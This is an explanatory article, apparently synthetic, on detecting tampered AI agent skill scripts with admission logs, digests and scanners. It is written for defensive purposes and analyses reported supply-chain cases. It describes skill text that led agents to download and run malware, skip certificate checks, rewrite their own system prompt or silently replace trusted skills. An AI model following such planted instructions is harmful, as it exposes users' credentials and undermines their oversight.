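# Detecting Tampered Skill Scripts in AI Agent Plugins with Admission Logs

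## What agent skills are and what an admission log records

An agent skill is a folder of written instructions, often with scripts and other files, that an AI agent loads when a task calls for it. An AI agent consists of a language model and an agent runtime, the program that loads skills and carries out the model's commands. An admission log is a lasting record of each decision to allow one exact version of a skill to be installed or loaded. Skills can change after someone approves them, and an approval is of little use later if nobody can tell which files it covered. A defender can check for changes by comparing fingerprints of the files now on disk with those in the log.

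The AI company Anthropic introduced the format in *Equipping agents for the real world with Agent Skills* (October 2025) and published it as an open standard two months later. Li, Wu and colleagues report in *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (2026) that the Agentic AI Foundation, under the Linux Foundation, now oversees the standard, and that several dozen agent products have adopted it, including Cursor, GitHub Copilot, Gemini CLI and OpenAI Codex. The same folder can therefore run under different runtimes with different safeguards.

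### Inside a skill folder

Only one file is compulsory. Under Agent Skills' *Specification*, a skill is a directory with at least a text file called SKILL.md, which has two parts. A short header gives the skill's name and a description, of at most 1,024 characters, of what the skill does and when to use it. Below the header come the instructions, in ordinary prose, with no restrictions on format. Authors can add a `scripts/` directory for code, `references/` for documentation, `assets/` for templates and data, and any other files they like. A skill for handling PDF files, which Anthropic uses as an example in its documentation, looks like this:

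```
pdf-processing/
├── SKILL.md          header and main instructions
├── FORMS.md          guide to filling in forms
├── REFERENCE.md      detailed technical reference
└── scripts/
    └── fill_form.py  program that the agent can run
```

The header contains little that helps detect tampering. It doesn't require a version number, though an author may put one in a free-form `metadata` field, where "1.0" is just text. The specification also doesn't define a field for file fingerprints or a signature. An author could store these in the folder anyway, but anyone who can alter the script can usually alter other files there too, so the record of what somebody approved has to be kept elsewhere.

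### From publication to a running script

Suppose the author of `pdf-processing` publishes it in a code repository or on a marketplace. The major community marketplaces require no security review before publication, according to Li and colleagues, while Anthropic checks each version of a plugin before listing it in its own directory. A user then installs the skill, which in the simplest case means copying the folder to a place where the runtime looks for skills. A skill can also depend on packages from one or more package managers, such as npm, pip and cargo, and *skills registry threat models* (2026) points out that installing the skill can then trigger install commands in each of them, for a manifest the user never read.

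A skill loads in stages, which Anthropic's *Agent Skills* illustrates with the PDF skill. At startup, the runtime puts only the skill's name and description into the model's context (the text available to the model), which uses about 100 tokens (units of text, roughly word fragments) per skill. The user then asks for the text of a PDF and a summary. The model matches the request to the description and reads SKILL.md with a shell command. It doesn't read FORMS.md because the user didn't ask for a completed form. If the user had asked for one, the model would have read that file too and might have run `fill_form.py`.

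The two parts of a skill work differently at this last step. The text of SKILL.md enters the context, and the model acts on it. A script runs as an ordinary program that the model starts through the shell. The model receives only the script's output, perhaps a line reporting that validation passed. It might balk at a strange new instruction in SKILL.md, but it has no comparable chance to object to a strange new line in `fill_form.py` unless it opens the file and reads the source code.

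The runtime determines what a running script can do. On Anthropic's API, skills run in a container without network access. In Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, they have the same network access as any other program on the user's computer, and Anthropic advises users to treat a new skill like newly installed software. Runtimes often prompt the user before running a command, but a skill's header can turn off some of these prompts. Anthropic's *Extend Claude with skills* gives the example of a chart-drawing skill whose `allowed-tools` field pre-approves the command that runs its `render.sh` script. Because this approval matches the command, which contains the script's path, a rewritten `render.sh` at the same path still runs without a prompt. Li and colleagues found that Claude Code applies the `allowed-tools` field, while Anthropic's toolkit for building agents ignores it.

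### Plugins and tool servers

Skills often arrive inside a larger package. Anthropic defines a Claude Code plugin as a directory of components that the runtime installs and loads as one unit. A plugin may contain skills, definitions of helper agents, settings for tool servers, and hooks, which are commands that the runtime runs at fixed points, such as after every file edit. Most plugins come from a marketplace, a catalogue that lists plugins and where to fetch them.

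A skill's script usually runs only after the model has picked the skill and decided to run the script. A hook runs whenever its event occurs, whatever the model has picked, and an enabled plugin is part of every session. Kapner (2026), in *Securing Claude Code plug-ins*, says this gives third-party code full access to the terminal, local files and environment variables, where programs often keep passwords and access keys.

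A plugin's manifest, `plugin.json`, contains metadata and settings for the plugin's components. A different kind of manifest is useful for detecting tampering. It lists the package's files with a fingerprint of each, and sometimes the permissions the package declares.

A tool server offers an agent a set of defined operations, usually through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard from 2024. The model calls an operation such as "search" or "create ticket" with typed parameters, and the server runs it. *A Systematic Survey of Agentic Skills* (Badhe, Shah and colleagues, 2026) treats a bare operation as a tool, which becomes part of a skill when somebody wraps it in a procedure that specifies which steps to take, in what order, and what to do if one fails. The survey rates tools as verifiable before use because they have schemas, and skills as only partly verifiable. But file comparison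 may work less well for tool servers than for skills, because if a server runs on somebody else's machine, its operator can replace the code without changing any files on the user's disk.

### Admission and its record

Li and colleagues observe that when users install a skill, they approve its identity, not a committed version of its content. An author, or an attacker who has taken over the author's account, can then change the skill and keep the trust users gave the earlier version. The runtime also reads the instructions and scripts without comparing them with what the user approved. Admission in the strict sense closes the first gap by tying approval to particular files, and comparing the files with the approved versions at load time closes the second.

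Different parties can decide whether to admit a skill. In *Agent Skill Security* (2026), the repository decides, examining each skill when it arrives and again at each update. It first applies fixed rules to check whether the skill has a developer signature, the publisher is on the trusted list, the version number has increased and the package matches its fingerprint. A language model then checks whether the skill's description, permissions and instructions are consistent with each other. Cisco's *Admission gate* makes the decision on the system that receives the skill. Its software watches for new skill and plugin directories, checks lists of blocked and allowed items, runs a scanner and applies a policy to the result.

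An admission record needs roughly the same contents no matter who makes the decision. The table shows an example entry for the PDF skill, with invented details.

| Field | Example entry | What a later investigator gets from it |
|---|---|---|
| Name and version | `pdf-processing`, 1.0 | The entry to compare against |
| Source | Repository address and commit | A place to fetch a clean copy |
| File digests | One SHA-256 value for each of the four files | Which files have changed, vanished or appeared |
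| Check results | Scanner, its version, its findings | What the approver knew |
| Approver | A named reviewer, or an automatic policy | Someone to ask |
| Time | Date and hour of the decision | Where the decision falls in the order of events |
| Decision | Admitted | Whether the files had permission to be there |

The source should have its own field because two skills can share a name. According to Anthropic's documentation, if Claude Code finds a skill called `deploy` in both the user's home folder and the project, it runs the one in the home folder. The check results matter most when someone has overruled them. With Cisco's gate, an administrator can exempt a skill from automatic enforcement by putting it on the allow list, but the scan result stays in the audit trail, so a colleague can later see that the skill was admitted despite a warning.

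*Sealing the Audit-Runtime Gap for LLM Skills* (Shen, Feng and colleagues, 2026) describes a more elaborate record, kept by a registry called SIGIL in which a committee votes on every skill. The registry stores the skill's content or a fingerprint of it, its permissions, the audit report and the version history. It also stores the reviewers' identities, their individual votes and the outcome. A loader on the agent's side checks each skill against this record before any of the skill's text reaches the model.

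An admission log differs from a log of what the agent does afterwards. *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts* (Metere, 2026) proposes an audit log that mostly records the agent's actions. Whenever an agent requests an irreversible action, such as sending an email, the runtime records the request, then the decision, then the execution or the error, all under one shared number. Refusals to load a skill go into the same log, so a single file can hold both kinds of entry. Suppose `fill_form.py` passes review on Monday and on Thursday sends a customer's tax form to an unknown server. A log of actions may show the transfer, but only the admission record can help establish whether Thursday's script was the one the reviewer read on Monday, and therefore whether the reviewer missed something or somebody changed the file.

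### What digests, signatures, pins and logs establish

A digest is a short fingerprint that a program computes from a file's bytes. SHA-256, the usual method, produces 64 hexadecimal characters whatever the file's length. The digest of a file that contains only `abc` begins with ba7816bf, and adding a `d` to the file changes those first characters to 88d4266f. Cryptographers designed SHA-256 so that nobody can feasibly find two different files with the same digest. If today's digest matches the recorded one, the file's contents are the same as when the digest was recorded. A match doesn't show that the file is safe, because a malicious script that the reviewer missed will also match its recorded digest.

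Anyone can compute a digest, including an attacker who has just altered a file. A signature requires a secret key, so it shows that someone with that key signed these exact bytes. In Metere's scheme, the signature covers the skill's files and its manifest, and the runtime refuses to load a skill if either has changed. Metere still considers a signed skill untrusted code until somebody has verified its behaviour, because a signature carries no information about what the code does. A signature also doesn't show that the signer was authorised to use the key or that the version is current. An old release with a known flaw keeps its valid signature, so Metere also has the runtime reject an older version once it has seen a newer one.

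Pinning fixes an installation to one version, commit or digest. The `version` field in a Claude Code plugin is text that the plugin's author chooses, and according to Anthropic, it generally pins the plugin to that version until the author changes it. Two different sets of files could carry the same version. A digest pin is stricter because any change to the files breaks the match. Pinning holds back security fixes as well as unwelcome changes, and it covers only what the pin names. SafeDep's *Agent Skills Threat Model* describes a harmless script that requests the latest release of an outside package each time it runs. The code that executes can change even though the script stays identical.

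An admission log records who decided what, when, and on what evidence. Without one, a defender who finds an unfamiliar digest cannot tell an approved update from a tampered file. The log is evidence only if nobody can edit it undetected. Techniques such as hash chains and transparency logs are meant to ensure this, though even an unaltered entry may record a bad decision.

### Other names for the record

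"Admission log" is not a standard term, and similar records go by other names. Shen and colleagues call it a registry record. The skill *agent-supply-chain*, on skills.sh, produces an "integrity manifest", a file of SHA-256 digests to compare with the plugin directory later. The changelog entry *fix(security): harden npm plugin and hook install integrity flow*, from the agent project OpenClaw, refers to an install record; the data saved at installation include the package's name, version, integrity value, checksum and time. Lockfiles, in which package managers record the exact releases they installed, contain much of the same information. A digest list or an install record can reveal that a file has changed, but it cannot show that anyone approved the original unless it also records who made the decision and what they decided.

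*Learning by Doing* (2026) uses "admission" in a second sense, for accepting skills compiled from an agent's own verified work. Its gates test the evidence behind each skill, its applicability and its conflicts with other skills. Each admitted change creates a version that nobody can alter. *Certifying That an Agent Skill Helps* (2026) describes a statistical test of whether skills improve an agent's results and a hash-chained ledger that records changes to the test plan. A skill that passes this test could still contain a script that copies passwords.

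## How skill scripts are changed after review

After a reviewer approves `pdf-processing`, its files pass from the author's repository through a marketplace and over a network to a folder on the user's disk, where later updates may replace them. Someone can alter the files at each of these points before the agent runs `fill_form.py`, though the access required varies considerably. Comparing the files with the admission log reveals only changes to bytes that the log covers.

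### Three situations that reports merge

Security reports tend to use "malicious skill" for three situations. In the simplest, the author publishes a skill that is already malicious. If a reviewer misses the harmful code and admits the skill, comparing its files with the admission log later won't reveal the problem, because the recorded files are also harmful.

A skill may be harmless when the reviewer reads it, but somebody can change its files afterwards. Comparing the files with the admission log can reveal this tampering.

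The files can also stay the same while remote content they use changes. For example, a script might always fetch the latest release of an outside package, or a SKILL.md might send the agent to a setup guide on a web page, which the page's owner can rewrite after the review.

In the definition of tampering, "unauthorised" means not approved by the person who admitted the skill. The hosting site allows developers to edit skills in their own repositories, but the person who admitted the skill approved only the earlier files, so an edit remains unauthorised until somebody reviews it. These edits matter because some attackers own the repository from the beginning and wait until the skill has been admitted before changing it.

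### The author's account and repository

Anyone who can write to the author's repository can change any file in the skill, and everyone who installs or updates the skill afterwards receives the change. The people with this access include the owner, colleagues with write permission, and anyone who has stolen one of their passwords or access keys.

A campaign that the agent-security company Zenity disrupted in August 2026 required even less, because the attacker never had to break into anyone's account. According to Zenity Labs' *Attackers Target Agents via The Skill Supply Chain*, on 2 July a GitHub user named karli-paperclip created an organisation with a name closely resembling that of Paperclip, a popular AI tool, and then copied Paperclip's entire source code into it, including the skills. By 5 July the copied skills had appeared on skills.sh, a public skill directory run by the company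 Vercel, and one was already listed with 2,264 installs. The skill files still matched the originals, so anyone reviewing them that day would have approved harmless text.

The attacker then made the repository malicious in steps. On 6 July, new code that fetched and ran a program from the attacker's server appeared in Paperclip's server program, which was in the same repository but outside the skill folders. On 11 July, the attacker put identical copies of a document, `setup-installation.md`, in seven places among the skills. In it, the attacker told agents that fetching and running the program was part of the supported way to install Paperclip. On 30 July, the attacker added a script that fetched and ran the program automatically during installation. The program searched 127 file locations on Mac and Unix machines for passwords and access keys.

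If a defender had recorded a digest of every skill file on 5 July, a check on 6 July would have passed, because the new code lay outside the skill folders. A check on 11 July would have failed at `setup-installation.md`. This setup guide was a page of prose, but it got the agent to run a script. A defender who had recorded only the main SKILL.md files might have missed the change even on 11 July, because those files described legitimate tasks and sent the agent to the setup guide only when Paperclip needed installing or starting.

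Zenity noticed the skills late on 1 August, and Vercel and Microsoft, which owns GitHub, removed them within 12 hours of its report. By then, the skills.sh counters for the family added up to more than 1.7 million installs, with individual skills near 300,000. Because the skills shared a repository and referred to one another, a single user may account for several installs, and Zenity doesn't know how many victims there were.

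Outside evidence supports other parts of the account. Internet Archive captures show the skills on the directory's trending list during July. The same attacker also published two Python packages with similar malware. An independent researcher reported both, the first together with Amazon's scanning service. The reports came in under two hours for one package and under one hour for the other, while the altered skills stayed up for three weeks.

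An attacker with a stolen access key can also change somebody else's repository. In a campaign called TrojanPony, which the startup AIR Security disclosed on 26 November 2026, the attacker used a developer's stolen GitHub token to add malware to 20 of that developer's repositories, including one with 3,300 stars, according to ThreatRoundup's *Fake ‘Improved’ Claude Skills Are Planting a Windows Trojan* (2026). The attacker also added an automated job that sent the projects' stored secrets to a Telegram chat. ThreatRoundup describes the 20 as legitimate developer repositories, not as skills, so they are good evidence of what an attacker can do with a stolen token but weaker evidence that anyone has altered a trusted skill this way.

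About 4% of the repositories in TrojanPony were hijacked. AIR counted 487 public repositories that carried the malware on 26 November. *速查：专盯AI Skills的新型攻击肆虐网络，超480个开源仓库沦陷* (2026), from the Chinese technology news site IT之家, lists 413 surviving forks (copies under other accounts) of malicious skills, 51 repositories connected with a fake PC version of the game GTA VI, the 20 hijacked repositories, and three fraudulent AI desktop apps.

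The skills themselves were malicious from the start. Since July the attacker had been publishing "improved" copies of popular skills such as ponytail, which worked like the originals but also installed a password-stealing trojan on Windows. Each copy included a genuine program that loaded a malicious library from the same folder. The program's signature was valid but did not cover the library. If a reviewer had admitted one of these skills, the malicious library would have passed every later comparison with the log.

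The figure of 487 comes from AIR, which sells products that vet agent add-ons. Others have confirmed parts of AIR's account. Zahn's *Fake Claude Code skills install a Windows password stealer* reported that the fake ponytail skill was still on skills.sh on 29 November, three days after AIR's disclosure, with passes from three security scanners. The malware-tracking project abuse.ch also lists the trojan, as MopsStealer.

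Stolen GitHub accounts are fairly common. TechRadar's *Thousands of GitHub repositories targeted in widespread attack* reported in November 2026 that attackers had used 4,837 compromised accounts to open pull requests in 61,764 repositories. A pull request only proposes a change, so those repositories weren't necessarily altered, and the attack wasn't aimed at skills in particular. But each compromised account may also have had write access to its own repositories.

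If a developer renames or deletes a GitHub account, an attacker may be able to register the old name without stealing any credentials. A marketplace that identifies a skill only by its web address could then fetch the attacker's files under the old listing.

### Marketplace listings and updates

Some marketplaces store a copy of each skill. An attacker needs access to the publisher's marketplace account or the marketplace's own systems to change that copy, and the author's repository can stay clean. A defender who compares the installed files only with the marketplace's current copy will find no difference, because both contain the attacker's change.

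Other marketplaces store only a listing, and the installer fetches the files from GitHub. Unless the user has pinned a commit, it usually fetches whatever is on the repository's main branch at that moment. The repository's owner can therefore change what new users receive without changing the marketplace listing, which still shows the installs, stars and scan results from the harmless version. The Paperclip copies' skill files became malicious six days after their first recorded installs on skills.sh.

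A time-of-check-to-time-of-use gap is the period between checking something and using it, during which it can change. The cloud security company Orca Security tested how wide this gap was on a prominent skill marketplace, which it doesn't name. According to a summary of Orca's findings published in May in AppSec Adventures' *Skill Issues* (2026), the marketplace scanned a skill when first listing it, and again only when the skill passed a certain level of popularity. Between the two scans, the page kept showing the first result.

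Orca's researchers then exploited the gap by submitting a harmless skill, waiting for it to pass, and immediately adding malicious instructions to the repository. They also inflated its install count to several thousand, which was easy because the marketplace accepted install reports from anyone. Real users installed the altered version while its page still displayed the clean result. The marketplace eventually flagged the skill, but it had already spread widely.

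If the counters on skills.sh were as easy to inflate in July as those on Orca's marketplace, some of the 1.7 million installs in the Paperclip figures may never have happened.

Users who installed the harmless version are safe from a change like this until they update. The attacker needs no access to a user's computer, because the user runs the update command that overwrites the files on disk. On the marketplace that Orca tested, this command could only update all installed skills together, and users couldn't view the differences beforehand or pin a skill to a version. One of Orca's attack sequences relied on this update process. The author attracts users with a useful skill, waits days or weeks, and then adds the malicious part, which reaches each user at their next update.

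Orca's test skills sent back the network address and name of each machine that ran them. The company concludes from this data that all three of its attack sequences, including the one that used updates, led to code running on real users' machines. It published an image of the log, with one line per machine, but gave no total. Others could in principle check the findings about the marketplace's design, although this is difficult without the marketplace's name, but they have only Orca's account of what ran on users' machines.

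A legitimate update also causes a mismatch. If the `pdf-processing` developer fixes a bug in `fill_form.py`, the new script needs another review, and a new log entry if the reviewer accepts the change.

### The download and the local copy

To alter a skill during download, an attacker must control the server that delivers it, a mirror or cache in between, or the user's network connection. Encryption makes tampering through the network connection difficult if the user's software checks the server's identity. The setup guide in the Paperclip copies told agents to skip that check, so a stranger on the same network could in principle have replaced the attacker's program with a different one.

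A more practical danger is that the downloaded package may never have matched the public source code. According to Zenity Labs, the public repository for paperclip-ai, one of the attacker's two Python packages, contained what looked like an ordinary command-line program for Paperclip. Instead of building the package from that code, the publishing process released a file that the attacker had uploaded by hand, which contained the password stealer. A reviewer who read the repository and recorded its digests would have approved files that nobody installed. To do the same to an honest project, an attacker would need permission to publish releases, which isn't always the same as permission to edit the code.

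Once a skill is on disk, any program that runs with the user's permissions can usually rewrite it. The attacker might already have malware on the machine, or an account with write access to a shared folder that holds the skill. If the skill is stored inside a software project, a colleague with write access to the project can also alter it, and the user receives the altered file when they next fetch the team's changes. In the first two cases, only the local copy changes, so the author's repository and the marketplace show no sign of the change.

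Ordinary programs unrelated to an agent can also alter its setup. Zahn mentions that Postman, a tool for testing web services, added itself to Claude Code without asking, though this didn't involve tampering with a skill script.

A user can also replace a skill by accident. On the marketplace that Orca tested, installing a skill silently overwrote any installed skill of the same name, even one from a different repository. To exploit this, an attacker would have to persuade the user to install from the wrong place, which a familiar name makes easier. If a user has an approved skill called `pdf-processing` and installs another with that name, the folder keeps its name but its contents may be entirely new. The replacement would not show up in a log that recorded only names, but the source and digest would both fail to match if the log included them.

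### An edit by the agent itself

An agent that can write files can often write to its own skills. An attacker can exploit this without an account or password by putting instructions in text the agent will read and follow, such as another skill or a web page it opens during a task.

Zenity (2026) reported two skills that exploited this. One told the agent to edit its system prompt, the standing instructions it receives at the start of a session, so that it would reinstall the skill if anyone deleted it. The other uninstalled skill-creator, a skill Anthropic supplies with Claude, and took its place without telling the user. Both examples come from a press release in which Zenity also launched a scanning service, and the release doesn't name either skill.

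The two examples differ in what the agent changed. When it replaced skill-creator, it changed the skill's own files, so a defender who had recorded their digests could detect the substitution. In the other example, the agent changed its system prompt, which is outside the skill folder, so every file in the skill could still match its digest. A defender who deleted the skill and then saw it return might have to look well beyond the admission log to find out why.

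Orca achieved a similar replacement in its tests. It listed a second skill whose instructions made the agent install a third with install reporting turned off, so the marketplace's data contained no trace of that installation. The third skill had the same name as a widely used skill from the marketplace's operator, and overwrote it. The user had agreed to install only the second skill, but the agent also replaced one they already trusted.

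Agents also edit skills for good reasons. A user may ask the agent to fix `fill_form.py` after it fails on a certain PDF, and the agent may save the repaired script in the skill folder. No reviewer has seen the new code, so a company that requires review before admission would count the repair as an unapproved change, even though the user asked for it.

### When only the linked content changes

AIR Security's test skill shows how an attacker can change a skill's result without changing its files. The Hacker News (2026) reported in June that AIR had built a skill called brand-landingpage, which offered to make web pages with Google's design tool Stitch. AIR submitted it to a marketplace repository with about 36,000 stars and 156 skills, and the maintainers accepted it after a few days. AIR then advertised the skill on Instagram to marketers, salespeople and designers.

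The skill told the agent to install the Stitch software by following setup instructions outside the skill, at a web address that looked like Google's but belonged to AIR. At first, the address led to the genuine documentation. After many people had installed the skill, AIR replaced the page with one that told agents to download and run a script. The script only sent the user's email address to AIR, which used these messages to count the agents it had reached.

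Once users have installed the skill, an attacker who copies this method needs to control only the linked page. The attacker changes content on the web server, and possibly a program the agent downloads from it. SKILL.md stays the same, so its digest still matches, and rescanning the same files reveals no change unless the scanner also follows the link.

AIR says it reached roughly 26,000 agents, some of them on corporate accounts. The Hacker News warns that nobody has independently confirmed these figures and that AIR was about to launch its own skill marketplace. Gen Agent Trust Hub's *brand-landingpage* (2026), a scan result published on skills.sh, rated the skill safe on 23 April. The scan detected the link to AIR's site but misidentified the site as the vendor's own. On 2 May, Gen Agent Trust Hub also passed a skill of the same name in another repository, which may have been a further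 copy. These outside results support AIR's account of the bait, but they don't show how many agents later ran the script.

A stranger may be able to take over a link that was legitimate when the reviewer checked it, because domain registrations expire and anyone can then buy the name. Sequoia Capital's *Partnering with Air* describes a later project in which AIR found 925 live skills fetching software or instructions from dead links. AIR registered the links and, according to Sequoia, took control of about 134,000 agents that had installed those skills. Sequoia has invested in AIR, so its account isn't independent confirmation. The method is still plausible, and it is worrying for defenders because the skill's author may have done nothing wrong beyond neglecting a link.

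The Paperclip campaign combined both methods. The attacker changed files in the skills to send agents to a server whose contents the attacker could replace at will. A digest comparison could have revealed the new instructions, but not which program a given agent received on a given day.

### Counts of malicious skills

Several published counts of malicious skills can be mistaken for measures of how often tampering happens. The best-known come from the security company Koi, which scanned ClawHub, the marketplace for the OpenClaw agent. Koi first found 341 malicious skills among 2,857, or about 12%. By 16 February 2026 it had found 824 among more than 10,700, so the share had fallen to under 8%.

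ClawHub responded to the early findings by screening skills automatically and blocking those it judged malicious. Between February and May, Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, still found five malicious skills there that the screening had not blocked. This is to be expected, since Trail of Bits' *The sorry state of skill distribution* (2026) showed that attackers could evade marketplace scanners. Calculating a rate from Unit 42's count would require the number of skills examined.

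Other figures have denominators that are easy to misread. Island's *AgentBaiting* (2026) reports about 7,600 malicious GitHub repositories, of which more than 800, or roughly a tenth, posed as skills or tool servers. This doesn't mean that a tenth of agent add-ons are malicious. Similarly, Zenity found that over 30% of the skills it identified as dangerous used agents to download and run malware, which is not a percentage of all skills. An audit by the security company Snyk also counts ordinary security flaws, such as a password that an author left in a skill by mistake. Those flaws should be fixed, but they don't necessarily involve an attacker.

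Even an accurate count of malicious skills would not measure tampering after approval, because it describes a marketplace at one moment. A perfect scanner would have classed the Paperclip copies' skill files as harmless on 5 July and malicious on 11 July, but the second result would not have distinguished them from skills that were malicious when first uploaded. Most of the skills in a marketplace count may never have passed review, in which case no later change to them could count as tampering after approval.

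Measuring tampering requires following a group of admitted skills over time. Suppose a company admits 1,000 skills, checks their digests for six months, and finds that 40 have changed. Its log contains new approvals for 37, but nobody approved the other three. The rate of unapproved change is then three in 1,000 over six months, and investigators can look into how many of the three were attacks. None of the counts above comes from such a comparison, so they do not establish how common tampering with approved skills is.

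### What changed in each case

The last column of the table assumes that a defender recorded a digest of every file in the skill or repository when it first became available, and later compared the files in use with those digests.

| Case | What changed | Where it changed | Result of the comparison |
|---|---|---|---|
| Paperclip copies, Zenity Labs | Server code on 6 July, a setup guide in seven places on 11 July, an installation script on 30 July | The attacker's own GitHub repository | Skill files match on 6 July and fail from 11 July |
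| Skill altered after its scan, Orca Security | The skill's instructions | Orca's repository, behind an unchanged marketplace listing | Mismatch |
| Skill altered before an update, Orca Security | The skill's instructions | The author's repository, then the user's disk at the next update | Mismatch after the update |
| Skill overwritten by another of the same name, Orca Security | All the files of a trusted skill | The user's disk, where the agent installed the replacement | Mismatch |
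| Replacement of skill-creator, Zenity | A skill supplied by Anthropic | The agent's installed skills, changed by the agent | Mismatch, if the record included supplied skills |
| TrojanPony's fake skills, ThreatRoundup | Nothing had to change, as the malware was there from the start | Not applicable | Match |
| TrojanPony's 20 hijacked repositories, ThreatRoundup | Added malware and an automated job | One developer's GitHub repositories, through a stolen token | Mismatch |
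| AIR's test skill, The Hacker News | A web page that the skill linked to | A site that AIR controlled | Match |

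## Vetting a skill before it is admitted

Vetting has to come before recording, because an admission log preserves whatever version the approver accepted. If that version contains a password stealer, removing the stealer later would cause a mismatch.

### What each method examines

A defender can vet a skill in several ways, and a clean result means something different for each. They can read the files, scan them for known patterns, ask a language model to judge them, or run the skill in a sandbox, an isolated environment where it can do no damage. They can also use formal analysis, in which a tool derives limits on a program's behaviour from its code.

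| Method | What it examines | What a clean result means | What it can miss |
|---|---|---|---|
| Source review | Instructions and scripts, read by a person | The reviewer saw nothing objectionable | Compiled files, obscure code |
| Static scanning | Text and code, compared with fixed rules | No rule matched | Attacks that no rule describes |
| Model-based review | The apparent purpose of instructions and code | The model judged the skill acceptable | Text written to mislead the model |
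| Sandbox run | Actions during test runs | Nothing harmful happened in those runs | Behaviour that the tests didn't trigger |
| Formal analysis | Operations that a tool extracts from the files | No extracted operation exceeds the stated limits | Operations that the tool fails to extract |

Suppose someone has added a line to `fill_form.py` that sends completed forms to a stranger's server, but only in December. A careful reviewer might notice the line. A static scanner might flag the network call, but it could equally flag a legitimate call to a tax office. A language model might detect that nothing in the skill's description explains the call. A sandbox run in June would show no transfer. Formal analysis could show that the script can use the network without permission, if the tool recognises the call in the code.

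Few skills show signs that anybody has read them closely. *After the Party* (Xiong and Zhang, 2026) found that 77.86% of the 65,175 skills listed in June on ClawHub, the OpenClaw marketplace, had neither a star nor a comment. Even a star doesn't show that someone inspected the files. Many users depend on automated scanners.

### Scanners and their error rates

ClawHub uses three scanners. A static analyser searches text and code for patterns such as exposed passwords and dangerous commands. VirusTotal submits the skill's files to about 70 antivirus engines and reputation services. SkillSpector, from the chip company Nvidia, examines the skill's instructions and declared capabilities for ways an agent could do damage. A language model then weighs the three results and information about the skill's origin, and gives a single verdict.

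The scanners rarely agree. In *ClawHub Security Signals*, Koc, Rivera and colleagues (2026) found that all three scanners flagged only 468 of 67,453 skills (0.69%). VirusTotal flagged 150 of the 206 skills with a final verdict of "malicious", while SkillSpector flagged 14. SkillSpector also flagged about three quarters of the 25,504 skills with a "suspicious" verdict. A VirusTotal flag usually means that a file resembles known malware, whereas a SkillSpector flag often means only that a skill could cause harm. The verdicts can't show which scanner was right, because ClawHub's model based them partly on the scanners' results.

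Xiong and Zhang compared ClawHub's scanners with human judgement. Two people with security experience examined 180 skills without seeing the scan results, then settled their disagreements. The language-model scanner had flagged 61.06% of the skills they thought needed review, VirusTotal 25.11% and the static analyser 21.67%. The reviewers thought 24.16% of the skills that no scanner had flagged also needed review. A skill can need review without being malicious, so these weren't all missed attacks. The percentages are weighted estimates for a pool of 276 skills, and they may not hold for the whole marketplace.

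Results for a single product also vary widely. Four 2026 studies tested Cisco's open-source skill scanner: *MaliciousSkillBench*, *PyCache Trap* (Liao, Qin and colleagues), *Behavioral Integrity Verification for AI Agent Skills* (Wu, Li and Liu), and *The Devil Wears Markdown*.

| Study | Part of Cisco's scanner tested | Malicious skills caught | Harmless skills flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| *MaliciousSkillBench* | Local behavioural analysis | 2.5% | 1.1% |
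| Liao and colleagues | A configuration that uses a language model | 24.2% | 33.5% |
| Wu and colleagues | Behavioural analysis | 35% | 18.1% |
| *The Devil Wears Markdown* | Scanner with a small language model, Qwen3:8B | 85% | 67% |

The studies used different attacks, harmless skills and scanner settings. The choice of harmless skills alone may greatly affect the measured error rate. Liao and colleagues report that Cisco's scanner flagged one of 100 harmless skills in one set and a third of 200 in another. A published error rate is therefore a poor predictor of how a scanner will perform on a company's own skills.

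Many false alarms come from text that makes a skill safer. *When Skills Tell Agents Not to Ask* (2026) examined instructions that loosen or tighten human oversight of an agent. Depending on the configuration, between 13% and 29% of the flags from Cisco's scanner and SkillSpector were for instructions that tighten oversight. The researchers then asked the language model behind the scanners a narrower question about oversight, rather than whether the skill was malicious. Its F1 score, which falls with both missed cases and false alarms, was 0.65, compared with 0.36 for the best scanner configuration. Defenders who use a model as a reviewer should probably ask it specific questions, such as whether any instruction tells the agent to act without confirmation.

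Scanners can also mistake ordinary features for data theft. *Scientific Agent Skills* (2026) describes a library of research skills whose maintainers publish their scan output with a document explaining the findings. Several data-theft rules fire whenever a skill reads its own access key and calls its own service, which is how many online services work. But a similarly named rule flagged a real problem, which the maintainers fixed, so dismissing all such alarms would be a mistake.

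Even a fairly accurate scanner produces mostly false alarms when malicious skills are rare. Suppose 10 of 1,000 skills are malicious, and a scanner catches 90% of them while flagging 10% of the harmless ones. It flags 9 malicious skills and 99 harmless ones, so someone has to examine 108 skills to find the 9 malicious ones.

*SkillGate* (Yang, Fu and colleagues, 2026) presents a tool of the same name that reduces this burden by combining pattern matching with a language model. The tool first compares a skill file with 530 patterns and passes the file if none match. If any do, it sends the text around each match to the model, which decides whether to pass the file. On a test set of 1,650 files, SkillGate caught 76.9% of the malicious ones and flagged 1.13% of the harmless ones, while two static tools flagged 50.4% and 17.4% of the harmless files. About two thirds of the files never reach the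 model, which saves money but also lets through any malicious file that matches no pattern. The test assumed that attackers didn't know the patterns, although SkillGate's developers have published them.

### A small company's scan

In *Skills are the new npm install, so we scanned ours*, Alfred and Bob (2026) describe how Workloft, a company that runs a fleet of AI agents, used SkillSpector to scan 107 skills, plugins and sets of configuration files in its own setup. They treated the scanner itself as untrusted software. They pinned it to one commit, read its build files and ran it without access keys or a network connection. They also left its language-model mode off.

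SkillSpector reported 276 high or critical findings, and the company read them all. None revealed anything malicious. Seven were accurate, including four about older skills that told the agent to read a credentials file directly. The other 269, or 97.5%, were false alarms. Some pointed to documentation or uninstall instructions, and others to the company's own security hooks, which contained the password patterns they were meant to block. Another 5,174 alarms came from one rule about packages bundled with two plugins, and the company set those aside without reviewing them.

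Workloft then planted 10 malicious skills of its own and blocked any skill with a high or critical finding. This rule stopped nine. The tenth contained a JavaScript file that sent the machine's environment variables to a remote server, but SkillSpector rated this only a medium risk. SkillSpector's default setting, which fails a skill only if its overall risk score exceeds 50, would have passed four of the 10.

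The stricter rule would also have blocked 41 of the 107 real units, so Workloft treats a block as a request for human review. Ten planted skills are too few to give a reliable detection rate. The company also didn't read every file by hand, so it could have missed a malicious skill that caused no serious finding. Still, the case shows roughly how much work is involved, since somebody had to read 276 findings to identify seven accurate ones.

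### Comparing declared and actual behaviour

A reviewer can test a skill's files against its description. Behavioural integrity verification, a method from Wu and colleagues, does this systematically with a list of 29 capabilities, such as reading files, sending data over a network and using credentials. One part of the analysis reads the metadata and lists the capabilities that the skill declares, *D*. Another examines the code and instructions and lists the capabilities that they use, *A*. Both parts combine ordinary program analysis with a language model, which must quote the text that supports each capability it reports.

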